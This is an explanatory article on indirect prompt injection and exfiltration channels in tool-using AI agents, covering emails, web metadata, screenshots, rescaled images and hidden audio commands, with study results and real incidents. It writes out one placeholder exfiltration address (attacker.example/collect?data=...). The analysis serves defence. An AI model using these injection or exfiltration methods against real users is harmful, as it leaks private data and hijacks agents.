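# Which input and output channels carry the most risk in tool-using AI systems

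## How a tool-using AI system takes in content and sends out data

An AI agent is a large language model connected to tools, software that lets it search the web, read a mailbox, open files or send messages. The model itself only reads text (and, in many systems, images) and writes text. Ordinary software around the model does everything else, from fetching a page to displaying a picture. Content reaches the model through inbound channels, and data leaves the system through outbound channels. Strangers can write to many of the inbound channels and receive data from many of the outbound ones.

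That combination makes indirect prompt injection and exfiltration possible. In indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in content that an AI system reads while doing a task for someone else. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced the concept in *Not what you've signed up for*, arguing that applications which retrieve outside text blur the line between data and instructions. They already listed email as one way to deliver such instructions. Exfiltration is the sending of private data to someone who should not have it. Microsoft (2025) describes it as one of the most widely reported results of indirect prompt injection, alongside unintended actions such as sending phishing links from the victim's own account. Microsoft adds that many injections are harmless, since any text in a model's input influences the output somehow.

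### One request, from inbox to screen

A user might ask a tool-using AI system to "summarise my inbox". Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), a design guide for developers, discusses a similar assistant, Email-Bot, which reads new messages from various senders, searches older mail for background and sends replies.

Before the model writes anything, the application assembles the context, which is all the text the model will read for its next step. It contains the developer's standing instructions and descriptions of the available tools, followed by the user's three-word request. At this point, only the developer and the user have influenced what the context contains. It has no emails yet, so the model first outputs a tool call, a short piece of structured text that the application parses and carries out, here by requesting unread messages from the mail server. The application adds those messages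 to the context and runs the model again.

The context now holds text written by colleagues, shops, mailing lists and anyone else who knows the user's address. It may also hold text from websites that the emails link to. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) points out that many assistants automatically fetch a preview of any link they come across, including the page's title and its metadata, the descriptive text that a website provides for machines. A person who opened the page would not normally see that metadata, but the model reads it alongside the user's request in a single, undivided context.

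Once the mail is in its context, the model either calls another tool or writes the summary. The summary is plain text with short codes for headings, links and pictures, and rendering turns it into what the user sees. The code for a picture, called a markdown image, contains the picture's web address, and the user's browser has to request the picture from that address to show it.

A single email summary can therefore set off several kinds of network request, though the user probably expected only the one to the mail server. The application contacts the mail server and may also fetch link previews. The agent may call a tool that reaches the web or sends a message. The browser loads any images referenced in the answer and sends another request if the user clicks a link.

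The answer a user sees on screen does not reliably show what data an agent has sent out. In 480 runs, Lan and colleagues asked a test agent to summarise a web page containing planted instructions, and recorded its network requests as well as its answers. The agent sent out private data in about 89% of runs, and checks on the visible answer missed 95% of the successful attacks. The 89% figure is not an estimate for current products, because the agent ran on a small model with seven billion parameters, its developer's instructions covered little more than the tool format, and the researchers had put the sensitive data directly in its context. Even without these conditions, an agent could send out data without mentioning it in its answer, because a tool call and a summary are separate outputs.

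### Why the model cannot reliably tell data from instructions

An obvious remedy would be to make the model treat emails as material to summarise and never as instructions. Other software does something similar. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C compares prompt injection with an older database flaw that could cause text typed into a web form to run as a command. Developers fixed that flaw with parameterised queries, which send the command and the user's text to the database separately, so that the database can never run the text.

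A language model does not separate instructions from data. It predicts the next token (a word or part of a word) from all the tokens so far. David C gives the example of a recruiter's tool that scores CVs. If a candidate hides an instruction in a CV, the model may follow it, even though the CV is meant to be data. David C prefers to call the model an "inherently confusable deputy", a component with real privileges that someone with fewer privileges can manipulate into using them.

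Special markers in the context show which text came from the developer, the user or a tool, and model makers train models to rank these sources in that order. These labels help less than one might hope. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) built probes, which are simple classifiers that read a model's internal activity, to estimate which source the model treats a passage as coming from. They trained the probes on identical text under different labels, so the probes could learn only from the labels. When they relabelled real user messages as tool output, the "user" score stayed at 76 to 88% across four models. It should have fallen to around zero if the labels determined how the models read the text. In a separate test of 1,000 attempts to make an agent send out a file, the success rate rose from 2% where the planted command scored lowest as "user" text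 to 70% where it scored highest. The probed models had 20 to 120 billion parameters, and larger ones might differ.

Behavioural tests also show that rank alone does not determine which instruction a model follows. *Position, Role or Label?* (Laddha, Pradhan and Srivastava, 2026) tested 14 open-weight models (models whose parameters anyone can download) on conflicting instructions from an operator, a user, a tool result and a saved note. The operator deploys the agent, and its policy should take priority. When the policy came first and a later instruction conflicted with it, the Qwen 3 models followed the policy in 6 to 17% of replies that followed one side or the other, and the Qwen 3.5 models in 12 to 42%. The two gpt-oss models, which OpenAI trained to respect the ranking, did so in 63 and 76%. The conflicts concerned mundane matters such as the naming of data fields, so these figures are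 not attack rates. At most 2.92% of the replies that followed one side flagged or hedged the conflict, so the user usually does not learn of it.

Models do not obey everything they read. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), most of the attacks on ChatGPT that the company knows of fail because training leads the model to refuse. The post also describes an emailed attack, reported by outside researchers in 2025, that worked 50% of the time in testing. How likely a model is to refuse depends heavily on the attack.

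### How a web address carries data out

Suppose a planted instruction does succeed. The data still needs a way out, and the simplest is a web address. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) illustrates this with a placeholder:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`

The part of a web address up to the first single slash names the destination. Everything after it goes to that destination as part of the request, and whoever writes the address can put any text after the question mark. Websites routinely log the addresses that visitors request, so the site's owner can read any private text in them, even if the requested page doesn't exist.

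If the address belongs to an image, the browser requests it as soon as the application displays the answer. Security researchers call this a zero-click leak because the victim does nothing beyond normal use. If the address belongs to a link, the browser doesn't send the data until the user clicks, so the leak is one-click. The user may notice something odd before clicking, or simply ignore the link.

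Chat apps often show a link preview, the title and picture that the app fetches when a link appears in a message. PromptArmor, a security company, notes that with previews on, a malicious link in an agent's message can leak data as soon as the message arrives, whereas without them the user would typically have to click the link. An app can therefore unintentionally remove the user's chance to avoid the leak by not clicking, even though the model writes the same text in both cases.

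### The lethal trifecta and the three-factor product

The programmer Simon Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, uses "lethal trifecta" for the dangerous combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally in one agent (Willison, 2025, *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*). The inbox assistant has all three, because it reads private mail, strangers write some of that mail, and it can send messages or display images.

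Meta's guide builds on this idea and uses Email-Bot to show what happens when a developer removes one property. If the assistant reads mail only from trusted senders, the planted instruction never reaches it. If it works in a test environment with no real mail, there is nothing worth stealing even if an injection succeeds. If it can write only to trusted recipients, or a person approves each draft, the stolen text does not reach the attacker. Meta concedes that human approval can fail when the user approves a warning without reading it.

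The trifecta shows whether a leak is possible. To compare channels one also needs some idea of how likely it is, and for that a product of three chances is useful:

$$P(\text{leak}) = P(\text{reach}) \times P(\text{obey} \mid \text{reach}) \times P(\text{exit} \mid \text{reach and obey})$$

The probability of a leak is the chance that an attacker's content reaches the model, times the chance that the model obeys it, times the chance that the model has a way to send data out. The first and last factors correspond to untrusted content and external communication in Willison's trifecta. Willison leaves out the middle factor, in effect treating obedience as something a careful developer has to assume. Private data isn't a factor because it affects how much harm a leak would do, not how likely it is.

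Each factor is conditional on the one before, as the vertical bars in the formula (read as "given") show, so multiplying three separately measured averages can mislead. For example, a filter that removes clumsy attacks from incoming mail lowers the first factor, but the remaining attacks are more persuasive, so the model will follow a larger share of those it reads. OpenAI's observation that such filters usually miss fully developed attacks suggests that this is a practical concern. The exit also depends on the earlier steps. If an agent can send email but not browse, the exit is open only to an instruction that asks for email. If the exit is a link, the third factor has to include the chance that the user clicks it.

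The product also gives the risk of only one attempt, and attackers can make many. If, to use invented numbers, half of an attacker's emails reach the model, the model obeys one in fifty of those, and the exit is always open, each email has a 1% chance of causing a leak. With a hundred independent attempts, the chance of at least one leak would be 1 − 0.99<sup>100</sup>, or about 63%. Real attempts are not independent, since a model that refuses one email will probably refuse a copy of it, but the arithmetic shows why Willison regards a security product that catches 95% of attacks as a failure by the standards of web security. If any factor is exactly zero, no number of attempts will cause a leak. In Willison's survey of more than a dozen leaks in commercial products, vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the exit. New exits keep appearing, and Willison (2026) still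 calls exfiltration the biggest challenge in designing agents.

### Five questions to ask of a channel

The three factors are hard to measure directly for most channels. Five simpler questions give a rough idea of them, and of how much damage a leak would do and how much effort a fix would take.

1. Who can write to it? Anyone can send an email, while only invited people can edit most shared documents. The writer need not be a criminal or a stranger. The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026) reported that Alibaba Cloud, an established provider, had been sending agents prompts that sought local data, as part of its measures against abuse. The company said it would stop.
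2. Does the user see it? People may spot a strange sentence in an email. They will not spot one in a page's metadata, or a request that the agent makes in the background.
3. Does it need a click?
4. How much data can it carry? A file can hold a whole mailbox, and a web address has room for a name or a password. At the far end is what Microsoft calls a covert channel, in which an outsider can observe whether the agent used a certain tool and so learns a single yes or no.
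5. What is lost by closing it? An assistant that ignores mail from strangers is safer and a good deal less useful. OpenAI makes a similar point about allowlists, which name the only destinations a system may contact. Rigid lists produce frequent warnings, and frequent warnings teach people to click through them.

The table lists the channels without ranking them by risk. It draws mainly on Microsoft's account, with additions from Greshake and colleagues, Lan and colleagues, Laddha and colleagues, and PromptArmor. An attack needs at least one channel from each half of the table, and they can be of different kinds. For example, an instruction can arrive by email and the data can leave through an image.

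| Direction | Channel | Who writes to it, or who receives from it | What the user does |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inbound | Web pages and search results | Anyone who can publish or edit a page | Asks for something that leads the agent there |
| Inbound | Page titles and metadata | Whoever controls the page | Mentions a link, or has the agent read one |
| Inbound | Emails | Anyone who knows the address | Asks the agent to read mail |
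| Inbound | Shared documents and files | Anyone who can share or edit them | Asks about the file |
| Inbound | Tool results, including code repositories | Anyone who can write to the service behind the tool | Sets a task that uses the tool |
| Inbound | Images, screenshots, audio and video | Whoever made the file or the page on screen | Has the agent look or listen |
| Inbound | Saved memory | Whoever wrote the content the agent saved earlier | Nothing new |
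| Inbound | Pasted text | The author of the copied text | Pastes it |
| Outbound | Images in a displayed answer | The server named in the image's address | Nothing |
| Outbound | Links in an answer | The server named in the link | Clicks |
| Outbound | Link previews in chat apps | The server named in the link | Nothing |
| Outbound | Web requests the agent makes | The server it contacts | Nothing, unless the application asks for approval |
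| Outbound | Emails and messages the agent sends | The recipient | Nothing, unless the application asks for approval |
| Outbound | Files, uploads and public repositories | Anyone who can read the place of storage | Nothing, unless the application asks for approval |
| Outbound | Covert signals from tool use | Anyone who can observe the effect | Nothing |

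## Instructions hidden in text the agent reads

Planted instructions can reach an agent through web pages, emails, support tickets, documents, code repositories and the results of its tools. These channels differ in who can write to them and how much of their text the user sees.

### What the user sees and what the model reads

A web browser displays only part of what a server sends. It leaves out programmers' comments, descriptions written for search engines, and HTTP headers, which are technical details sent before the page. A page's author can also hide ordinary text by matching it to the background colour, making it too small to see or placing it outside the visible area. White text on a white background is also invisible in an email or a PDF. Software that extracts text for a model may still pick up the hidden text because it remains in the file.

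What the model reads therefore depends on how the application prepares the page. Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, tested this with 100 different injections found on real websites. They gave 13 models each page in four forms and asked for a summary, which made 5,200 runs. The models followed the planted instruction in 3.9% of runs with plain text extracted from the page, 1.1% with its HTML source code, 1.1% with a snapshot of its structure after a browser had rendered it, and 0.2% with the server's complete response, including headers.

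The likely reason, according to Khodayari and colleagues, is that source code and snapshots preserve signs that a passage was hidden. Extraction removes those signs, so the planted instruction looks like any other sentence on the page. However, the rates for source code and complete responses are low partly because these inputs were too long for the model in 20.3% and 25.8% of runs respectively, so it failed to produce a usable answer. Snapshots caused such errors in only 3.5% of runs, which makes them better evidence that structure helps. In six runs, a model pointed out the planted instruction but still followed it.

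### Who can write to each carrier

Anyone can publish a web page, and even a well-known site may contain text its owner didn't write. About 80% of the injections that Khodayari and colleagues found were in the site operator's own content. Most of the rest were in material that other people publish through a site, such as job adverts, and 1.4% were in comments and similar contributions. *Notes from Underground*, a July 2026 report by the email security company Proofpoint on what criminals discuss and sell in closed forums, also describes plans to put instructions in adverts that load on other pages. One example used the text description attached to an image, which most visitors never see.

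An attacker needs only an address to send someone an email. The recipient sees the formatted message, while an assistant may also read any hidden text in it. Darktrace's *Testing a Prompt injection Attack Against an Enterprise AI Agent* (2026) describes a test email that contained a hidden instruction but no malware or malicious links, and came from a sender whose reputation raised no suspicion. A filter that checks only for malware and bad links would have missed it. Darktrace, which sells email security, reports that its own product caught the message because of its unusual language. Calendar invitations require even less from the recipient. In an example from Proofpoint, the invitation appeared in the recipient's calendar automatically, before it was accepted, with the instruction in what looked like the meeting agenda.

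Anyone who can fill in a support desk's contact form can write to the agent that sorts its tickets. Customer records are less obviously open to outsiders because staff maintain them, but they may include names, notes and answers that the customer typed in. An employee who asks an agent about that customer months later may see only a summary, while the agent reads the whole record. A successful injection could also do more damage here than in a tool that only summarises web pages because, as Khodayari and colleagues point out, support agents may have access to user data, internal systems and transactions. Support agents also appeared to be the main targets of the few injections in their sample that were meant to extract secrets.

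Users often upload documents that someone else wrote, such as contracts, invoices and CVs. Proofpoint shows a PDF, generated with a criminal tool, that opens as an ordinary non-disclosure agreement but contains an instruction in its underlying file to send spreadsheets to an outside address. None of the scanners on VirusTotal, a service that checks files for malware, flagged the PDF. Proofpoint thinks it debatable whether an agent would act on text in that part of the file, though the same criminals were also testing white text on the visible page.

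Coding agents read source code, documentation and bug reports. On a public project, outsiders can usually file a bug report without anyone's approval, but a maintainer has to accept changes to the code. The developer could read all of this material but rarely does, since people use agents largely to save that effort. *The Summer of Johann* (Willison, 2025) describes how the security researcher Johann Rehberger published a report every day in August 2025 on prompt injection flaws in AI tools, including the coding agents Cursor, Claude Code, GitHub Copilot and Google Jules.

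Someone else can also gain control of the page behind a trusted link. Some websites publish a file called llms.txt, which directs AI systems to useful documentation. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code*, from August 2026, reports that researchers found references to unclaimed addresses in such files on 120 domains. Anyone who claimed one of those addresses could decide what agents read there without breaking into the website that linked to it.

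Agents receive much of this material as tool results, which also include search listings, database entries and replies from other companies' services. Anyone who can add text to one of these sources can use it to reach the agent, and the user may see only a note that the agent called the tool. Gavish (2026) warns in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that instructions planted in an assistant's data or tools may take effect without any input from the user.

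### How much the place on the page matters

In the *Silent Egress* experiment, Lan and colleagues compared four places where an attacker could put an instruction on a web page: the body, the title, the text of a link and the metadata. They had their test agent summarise the page, reaching it through either a direct link or one that redirected through other addresses. For each combination of place and link, they tried a simple instruction, to send the secret in a single request, and a harder one, to send it in pieces. They ran each of the 16 configurations 30 times.

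For runs with a direct link, the table gives the share in which the agent sent at least one request to the researchers' collection server.

| Place of the instruction | Where a person would see it | Simple instruction | Harder instruction |
|---|---|---|---|
| Body | On the page, unless hidden | 100% | 76.7% |
| Title | In the browser tab | 100% | 83.3% |
| Link text | On the page | 100% | 83.3% |
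| Metadata | Nowhere on the page | 96.7% | 60.0% |

The simple instruction worked in 29 of 30 runs (96.7%) when it was placed in metadata, which visitors never see, so it did almost as well there as in the text of the page. With the harder instruction, metadata had the lowest success rate when the link was direct and tied with link text for the lowest, at 70%, when there were redirects. Thirty runs are too few to rank the other three places with any confidence.

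The agent contacted the collection server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%). It never did so in 120 further runs on harmless pages, so the planted text was clearly the cause. The 88.1% covers every run in which a request arrived, whether or not it carried the secret. With the simple instruction, the first request contained sensitive data in 96.7% of runs. The figures for the harder instruction are unreliable. Lan and colleagues report sensitive data in the first request in 26.3% of runs but anywhere in the first three requests in only 15.8%, which is impossible because the first three include the first.

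A user would not have seen an instruction that their agent read in the metadata. They would usually have seen no sign that the attack had worked either, because the visible answer looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks.

Lan and colleagues call their setup attacker-favourable, but they did not try to disguise the planted instructions, so a more skilled attacker might have done better. They also suggest that larger models could be more vulnerable, because a model that is better at following instructions and using tools might also carry out planted instructions more reliably.

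Khodayari and colleagues found much lower rates. Small models followed 4.2% of the injections taken from real websites, and closed commercial models followed 0.6%. But the models only had to write a summary and had no secret to give away, and many of the injections asked only for nonsense. The gap between 88.1% and these rates therefore reflects the attacks and the setups as well as the models. Neither experiment measures the risk for a commercial agent with access to someone's mailbox.

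### What researchers have found on the public web

Khodayari and colleagues also made the most detailed count of injections outside the laboratory. They searched 1.2 billion web addresses from the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for about 4,000 phrases typical of prompt injection. They reviewed the matches to remove tutorials and news articles that only discuss the subject. They confirmed 15,387 injections on 11,722 pages, some of which came from two services that scan the internet for connected machines. The confirmed pages from Common Crawl amount to roughly eight per million addresses searched.

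The largest group of these injections, with 8,894, was meant to disrupt AI systems, mostly by making them produce random or endless text. Another 4,093 told AI systems not to reuse personal or copyrighted material, and 3,096 were meant to expose automated visitors, for instance by asking any AI that filled in a form to include a certain word. A further 1,521 promoted a product, a source or a job candidate. An injection could belong to more than one group. Only 13 were attempts to obtain confidential information, and nine of those asked for the system's standing instructions.

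About 87% of the injections were invisible to people. More than half of all the injections were in HTTP headers, so they would never reach a model that receives only the text of a page. Khodayari and colleagues found archived copies from a year earlier for 89% of the affected Common Crawl pages, and about two-thirds of those copies already contained an injection.

Visible injections are far more common in *Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 study by Unit 42, the research arm of the security company Palo Alto Networks. Plain visible text was the most frequent method in its data, at 37.8%. Headers explain only part of the difference, since only about 8% of the injections in the page itself that were still there when Khodayari and colleagues checked were visible. The two groups evidently sampled different parts of the web, so neither percentage holds for the web as a whole. Visible text can also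 go unnoticed. Unit 42 describes two cases in which the instruction was in the page's footer, where few people look.

Google scanned several editions of Common Crawl and reported in April 2026 that malicious injections had increased by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. It did not publish the number of malicious pages, so the increase could be very few pages. Only a small number of the injections aimed to steal data, and these were crude. One was apparently an experiment by the site's author. Google still expects such attacks to grow in scale and sophistication, because agents are becoming more capable and therefore more valuable targets.

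Both Common Crawl studies probably miss injections, since they began by searching for known phrases. The count of 13 attempts to obtain confidential information may be especially incomplete, because someone stealing data has more reason to avoid familiar wording than a site owner who wants to annoy scrapers. Common Crawl also leaves out most social media and everything behind a login. Google chose to study the public web partly because it is easy to observe. Nobody can scan the world's mailboxes, support queues and shared folders in the same way, so these counts are not evidence that attackers prefer web pages to email.

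### Criminal campaigns, tools for sale and the question of thefts

The clearest examples of criminals targeting agents come from *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, published by the security company Zscaler in July 2026. Zscaler found two live campaigns that used both text hidden from visitors and structured metadata meant for search engines. One was a fake documentation site for a Python library, which its operator had pushed to the top of search results. Hidden instructions on the site presented a $3 payment as a routine step towards fixing an error. The same operator had ten repositories on the code-sharing site GitHub that linked to similar sites.

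To see whether the scam could work, Zscaler built an agent with browsing and payment tools, gave it no spending limit and sent it to the site in a sandbox with no real money. It repeated the test with 26 models, and four of them paid: two versions of Meta's Llama and two of Google's Gemini.

The second campaign used a fake website for DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, with hidden text telling AI systems to treat it as the official site. No model accepted the fake when Zscaler also supplied the real site. Without the real site, GPT-5.4 accepted the fake when it was supplied with other sources, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 accepted it when it was the only page supplied. Comparing sources therefore gives an agent some protection, provided that one of them is genuine.

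It is unclear whether the payment scam ever fooled an agent. The attacker's cryptocurrency wallet had received payments, but they were larger than the amount the site requested, and Zscaler thinks they may have come from earlier attacks. Even a matching payment would have been weak evidence, because the site also showed its payment options to human developers. Zscaler's Amit Banker told SC Media that the attacker may have chosen the small price to avoid fraud alerts and stay within agents' spending limits. Neither campaign tried to steal private data, so while they show that criminals can get instructions in front of agents and that some models will follow them, they don't show that private data would leak.

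Other reports also describe attempts without confirmed victims. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* covers ten injections that the security company Forcepoint found on live websites. The attackers' aims included financial fraud, deleting data and stealing API keys, the credentials that programs use to access online services. Forcepoint's Mayur Sewani stressed that the harm depends on the agent's privileges, and rated a browser assistant that can only summarise as low-risk. In December 2025, Unit 42 found a scam advert whose page contained hidden instructions telling AI systems that review adverts to approve it. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case of such an attack fooling a working review system.

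Criminals can also buy tools to produce injections. According to Proofpoint, sellers on underground forums were advertising generators for emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages, with subscriptions starting at about $150 a month. At that price, people who could not design their own attacks would be able to buy them, but the adverts don't show that the tools work. Proofpoint called the techniques experimental and suggested that criminals had little reason to switch yet, since deceiving people still works well. In November, Underhill (2026) still noted in *Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* that Proofpoint had not established wide exploitation.

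None of these reports includes a confirmed case of a criminal stealing private data through an agent. This is less reassuring than it would be for most crimes, because a victim who checked only the agent's answers would probably not notice the theft. Detecting it would require a record of the agent's network requests.

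## Instructions hidden in images, screenshots and sound

Attackers can also plant instructions in the pictures and sound that an agent takes in.

### How a picture becomes an instruction

A multimodal model accepts images as well as text. It divides a picture into small patches, and a vision encoder converts them into numbers that the language model processes together with the user's typed words. Such models can read writing in pictures, which makes them useful for scanned contracts and photographed receipts. An instruction written on a receipt enters the same context as the user's question.

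A filter that searches text for suspicious phrases cannot detect instructions that exist only as pixels. This matters most for computer-use agents, which work from screenshots. In *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026), these agents receive no page text, so the benchmark tests text-based detectors only on browser-use agents, which also receive a list of the page's interactive elements.

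A detector can examine the screenshot instead, but general-purpose models vary widely at this. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) compares them by F1 score, a measure out of 100 that rewards catching injections and penalises false alarms. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite scored 83.2 on page text and 78.7 on screenshots, while GPT-5.4 nano fell from 78.4 to 37.5. Judging by its other scores, GPT-5.4 nano caught only about a quarter of the injections in screenshots. BrowseSafe-Guard, a purpose-built detector, scored 93.3 and raised false alarms on about 6% of harmless screenshots, so developers can close much of this gap.

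### Legible text, faint text and altered pixels

The simplest attack uses text that anyone could read, such as a line in a scanned document or a pop-up on a web page. A person might still miss it, especially if the agent is working unsupervised.

Attackers can also hide instructions in text too faint for people to notice, but the model must still be able to read it. *Image-based Prompt Injection* (Nagaraja, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested this on GPT-4-turbo by adding written instructions to ordinary photographs, directing the model to output a fixed word instead of describing the picture. With brightly coloured text, the 12 wordings succeeded in 73 to 100% of attempts. With text blended into the background, the best combination of wording and colouring succeeded in 64%. Two other ways of blending succeeded in at most 25% and 10% of attempts, because the model often couldn't read the text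 either. Very small lettering failed even in a bright colour, with no successes in 800 attempts at the smallest size.

The 64% figure is a poor guide to the risk of a leak. GPT-4-turbo is far older than current models, and it had no tools or private data in this experiment. The photograph was its only input, so there was no user request for it to follow instead of the planted instruction. Nagaraja and colleagues measured how much the image had changed but did not test whether people could see the blended text.

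A third kind of attack contains no readable text. The attacker makes small changes to many pixels, which together push the model towards a chosen output. *SnapGuard* (2026), a paper on detecting attacks in screenshots, treats these changes separately from written instructions. Searching the image for words would not reveal them, but they are harder to produce than written instructions. *Adversarial Images Hijack Web Agents from Visual Grounding to Browser Execution* (2026) describes an earlier attack, WebInject, that required access to the model's internals and control of the whole page. Someone who writes an instruction on a page needs neither. However, anyone can obtain the internals of an open-weight model.

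### Screenshots in the Comet browser

In October 2025, the browser company Brave published *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, by Chaikin and Sahib. It described a flaw that let prompt injections in faint text work against Comet, Perplexity's commercial AI browser. Comet's assistant lets users take a screenshot of a website and ask questions about it.

The instruction was nearly invisible text on a web page. When a user took a screenshot of the page, Comet extracted the text and passed it to the model without separating it from the user's question. Chaikin and Sahib suspected that Comet used text recognition software, but could not confirm this because its code is not public.

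The flaw exposed whatever the assistant could reach through the user's logged-in accounts, which might include email, banking and cloud storage. The planted instruction could direct the assistant's browser tools, so an attacker could have used them to send the data out. Brave did not report that anyone had stolen data this way.

Brave reported the flaw to Perplexity on 1 October and published the details on 21 October. Its timeline lists no reply or fix from Perplexity. Brave had a commercial interest in the subject because it competes with Perplexity and was planning agent features for its own browser.

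The same post describes a related flaw in Fellou, another AI browser. Fellou showed some resistance to hidden instructions but trusted visible page text, which reached the model when a user simply asked the browser to open a page. Chaikin and Sahib blamed both flaws on a failure to keep untrusted web content separate from the user's request. Attackers could exploit this weakness through Comet's screenshots, but they can also exploit it with ordinary text. The screenshot attack also required the user to take a screenshot of the page containing the hidden instructions, whereas a computer-use agent takes screenshots routinely.

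### Images that change when software shrinks them

Besides making text faint, an attacker can hide it from the user by making it appear only when the image is shrunk. AI applications often shrink large images before giving them to the model. Each pixel of the small version is a weighted mix of several pixels in the original, so someone who knows how the software mixes them can prepare a photograph that looks harmless to the user at full size but has writing on it in the version the model receives.

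Trail of Bits' *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025) shows that an instruction hidden in an image could leak a user's data. The security company's researchers connected Gemini CLI, Google's command-line assistant, to Zapier, a service that links applications. They then gave it a picture containing an instruction that became visible when the picture was shrunk. The model followed the instruction and used Zapier to send data from the user's Google Calendar to an attacker's email address. Gemini CLI didn't show the user a preview of the shrunken picture that the model saw, and it didn't ask for approval because the Zapier connection approved every tool call automatically.

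Trail of Bits researchers also got planted instructions through to the model in several other products, including Gemini's web interface, Google Assistant on an Android phone and Genspark, another company's AI agent. In Google's Vertex AI Studio, the screen showed the full-size picture instead of the version the model received, so even a careful user could not have spotted the text. The researchers described data being sent out only in the Gemini CLI test.

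Google did not treat the finding as a vulnerability in its product. According to AllMind AI's *Honey, I shrunk the image and now I'm pwned*, a summary for investors, Google acknowledged the research but said the attack required users to override the default safety settings. Trail of Bits said it had used the default configuration for the Zapier connection. Both statements can be true, because Gemini CLI and the Zapier connection have separate defaults. A user who followed Zapier's set-up could have turned off a safeguard in Gemini CLI without meaning to.

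Trail of Bits recommended that applications limit the size of uploads instead of shrinking them, or at least show users exactly what the model will see. It advised against just looking for a safer shrinking method, since the attack is not limited to the three common ones it studied. Its strongest recommendation was that text in an image should never be able to start a sensitive tool call without the user's explicit confirmation. This requirement would have stopped the calendar leak even if the model had obeyed the instruction.

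### Commands hidden in sound

An agent that takes input from a microphone also picks up other people, televisions and loudspeakers, so anyone close enough to the device can give it input without needing an email address or a website.

In *Piggybacking on Perception*, Liu, Li and colleagues (2026) studied attackers' commands that play while the user is speaking to an agent. They tested 11 models with 2,160 audio samples, covering eight everyday scenarios and ten ways of disguising the command. Some disguises used frequencies above human hearing, some distorted the speech until it resembled noise, and others left it audible but hard for the user to follow. The models worked in a sandbox with simulated tools, and an attack counted as successful if the model's response and tool calls followed the attacker's command.

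The attacks' average success rate was 49%. It varied much more between disguises, from about 6% to 82%, than between models, from 27% for Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite to 69.1% for Gemini 3 Pro. Flash-Lite's low rate is not clear evidence of better security, because the model probably misunderstands attackers' instructions as it often does users'. It completed only 42% of ordinary requests when there was no attack, compared with 93% for Gemini 3 Pro.

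These attacks also interfered with users' own requests. Models completed 76% of them correctly without an attack but only 25% with one. A user would therefore often notice that something had gone wrong, even without hearing the command.

Liu, Li and colleagues also tested the attack on a commercial phone built around the Doubao voice assistant. While the user asked about the weather and a travel route, a barely perceptible command told the assistant to share the user's live location. The assistant opened a map app, created a sharing link and texted it to the attacker's phone. The researchers reported the problem to the teams behind Doubao and Qwen, but do not say that either team confirmed or fixed it.

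The phone test shows that a leak is possible with a real device, but not how often it would happen outside a laboratory. Inaudible commands succeeded in about 60% of trials, but the trials used 20 volunteers from the researchers' own laboratory and a specialised loudspeaker and amplifier. In a separate test at half a metre, the average success rate fell from 69% when the loudspeaker faced the device to 28% when it was at a right angle. The benchmark also used another AI model to help judge success, which Liu, Li and colleagues acknowledge could have introduced bias.

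Separating the voices in a recording and blocking commands from a second speaker made all ten disguises less successful. But this defence also blocked 35% of harmless requests recorded over the noise of a meeting with several people talking, 14% over cafeteria noise, and at most 1.5% on a bus or in a park. An assistant for a quiet car could use this defence more easily than one for an open-plan office.

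### Comparing text, pictures and speech

These cases show that pictures and sound can carry instructions, but not whether they work better than text. To compare them, researchers have to present the same message in different forms.

Chen and Ghadiyaram (2026), in *A Systematic Study of Cross-Modal Typographic Attacks on Audio-Visual Reasoning*, did this with questions about videos. They chose a wrong answer to each question, suggested it to the model in typed text, on-screen words or added speech, and counted how often the model gave that answer. The table shows the results for MMA-Bench questions about what is visible in a video, and for WorldSense, a multiple-choice test that draws on both picture and sound.

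| Model | Visual questions: typed | Visual questions: on screen | Visual questions: speech | WorldSense: typed | WorldSense: on screen | WorldSense: speech |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Omni-7B | 58.69% | 50.34% | 24.27% | 76.90% | 73.22% | 60.57% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 1.91% | 5.80% | 2.43% | 36.64% | 49.82% | 48.33% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 0.76% | 2.60% | 0.76% | 53.82% | 56.72% | 43.41% |
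| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 0.76% | 1.53% | 0.15% | 46.56% | 41.01% | 32.18% |

Typed text misled Qwen most often. On-screen text misled all three Gemini models most often on the visual questions, and two of them on WorldSense. However, the Gemini rates on the visual questions are so low that they differ by only a few percentage points. The WorldSense rates partly reflect chance, since 10 to 18% of the models' answers matched the attacker's choice without an attack.

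These figures measure wrong answers, not harmful tool actions. A model that misidentifies an animal in a video would not necessarily send someone's email to a stranger. Chen and Ghadiyaram came closest to measuring actions in a test where Qwen chose tasks for a robot, though no robot carried them out. Misleading speech made Qwen choose the attacker's task in 25% of 200 trials, and speech combined with matching text in the camera image did so in 70%.

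Listeners always noticed the added speech at the volume used for the main results. At the lowest volume in the listening test, they missed it 77% of the time, but Qwen's rate on WorldSense rose only from 18.3% to 21.9%.

Two other studies compared how often models obey a command in typed text and in a picture. *Render Before Reading* (Zhang, Baroian and colleagues, 2026) used AgentDojo, a test in which agents use tools for tasks such as banking and travel. It gave each agent its tool results either as text or as a plain picture of the same text, with the same planted instructions. The table shows how often the agents carried out those instructions.

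| Model | As text | As a picture |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 90.0% | 49.2% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 83.1% | 41.5% |
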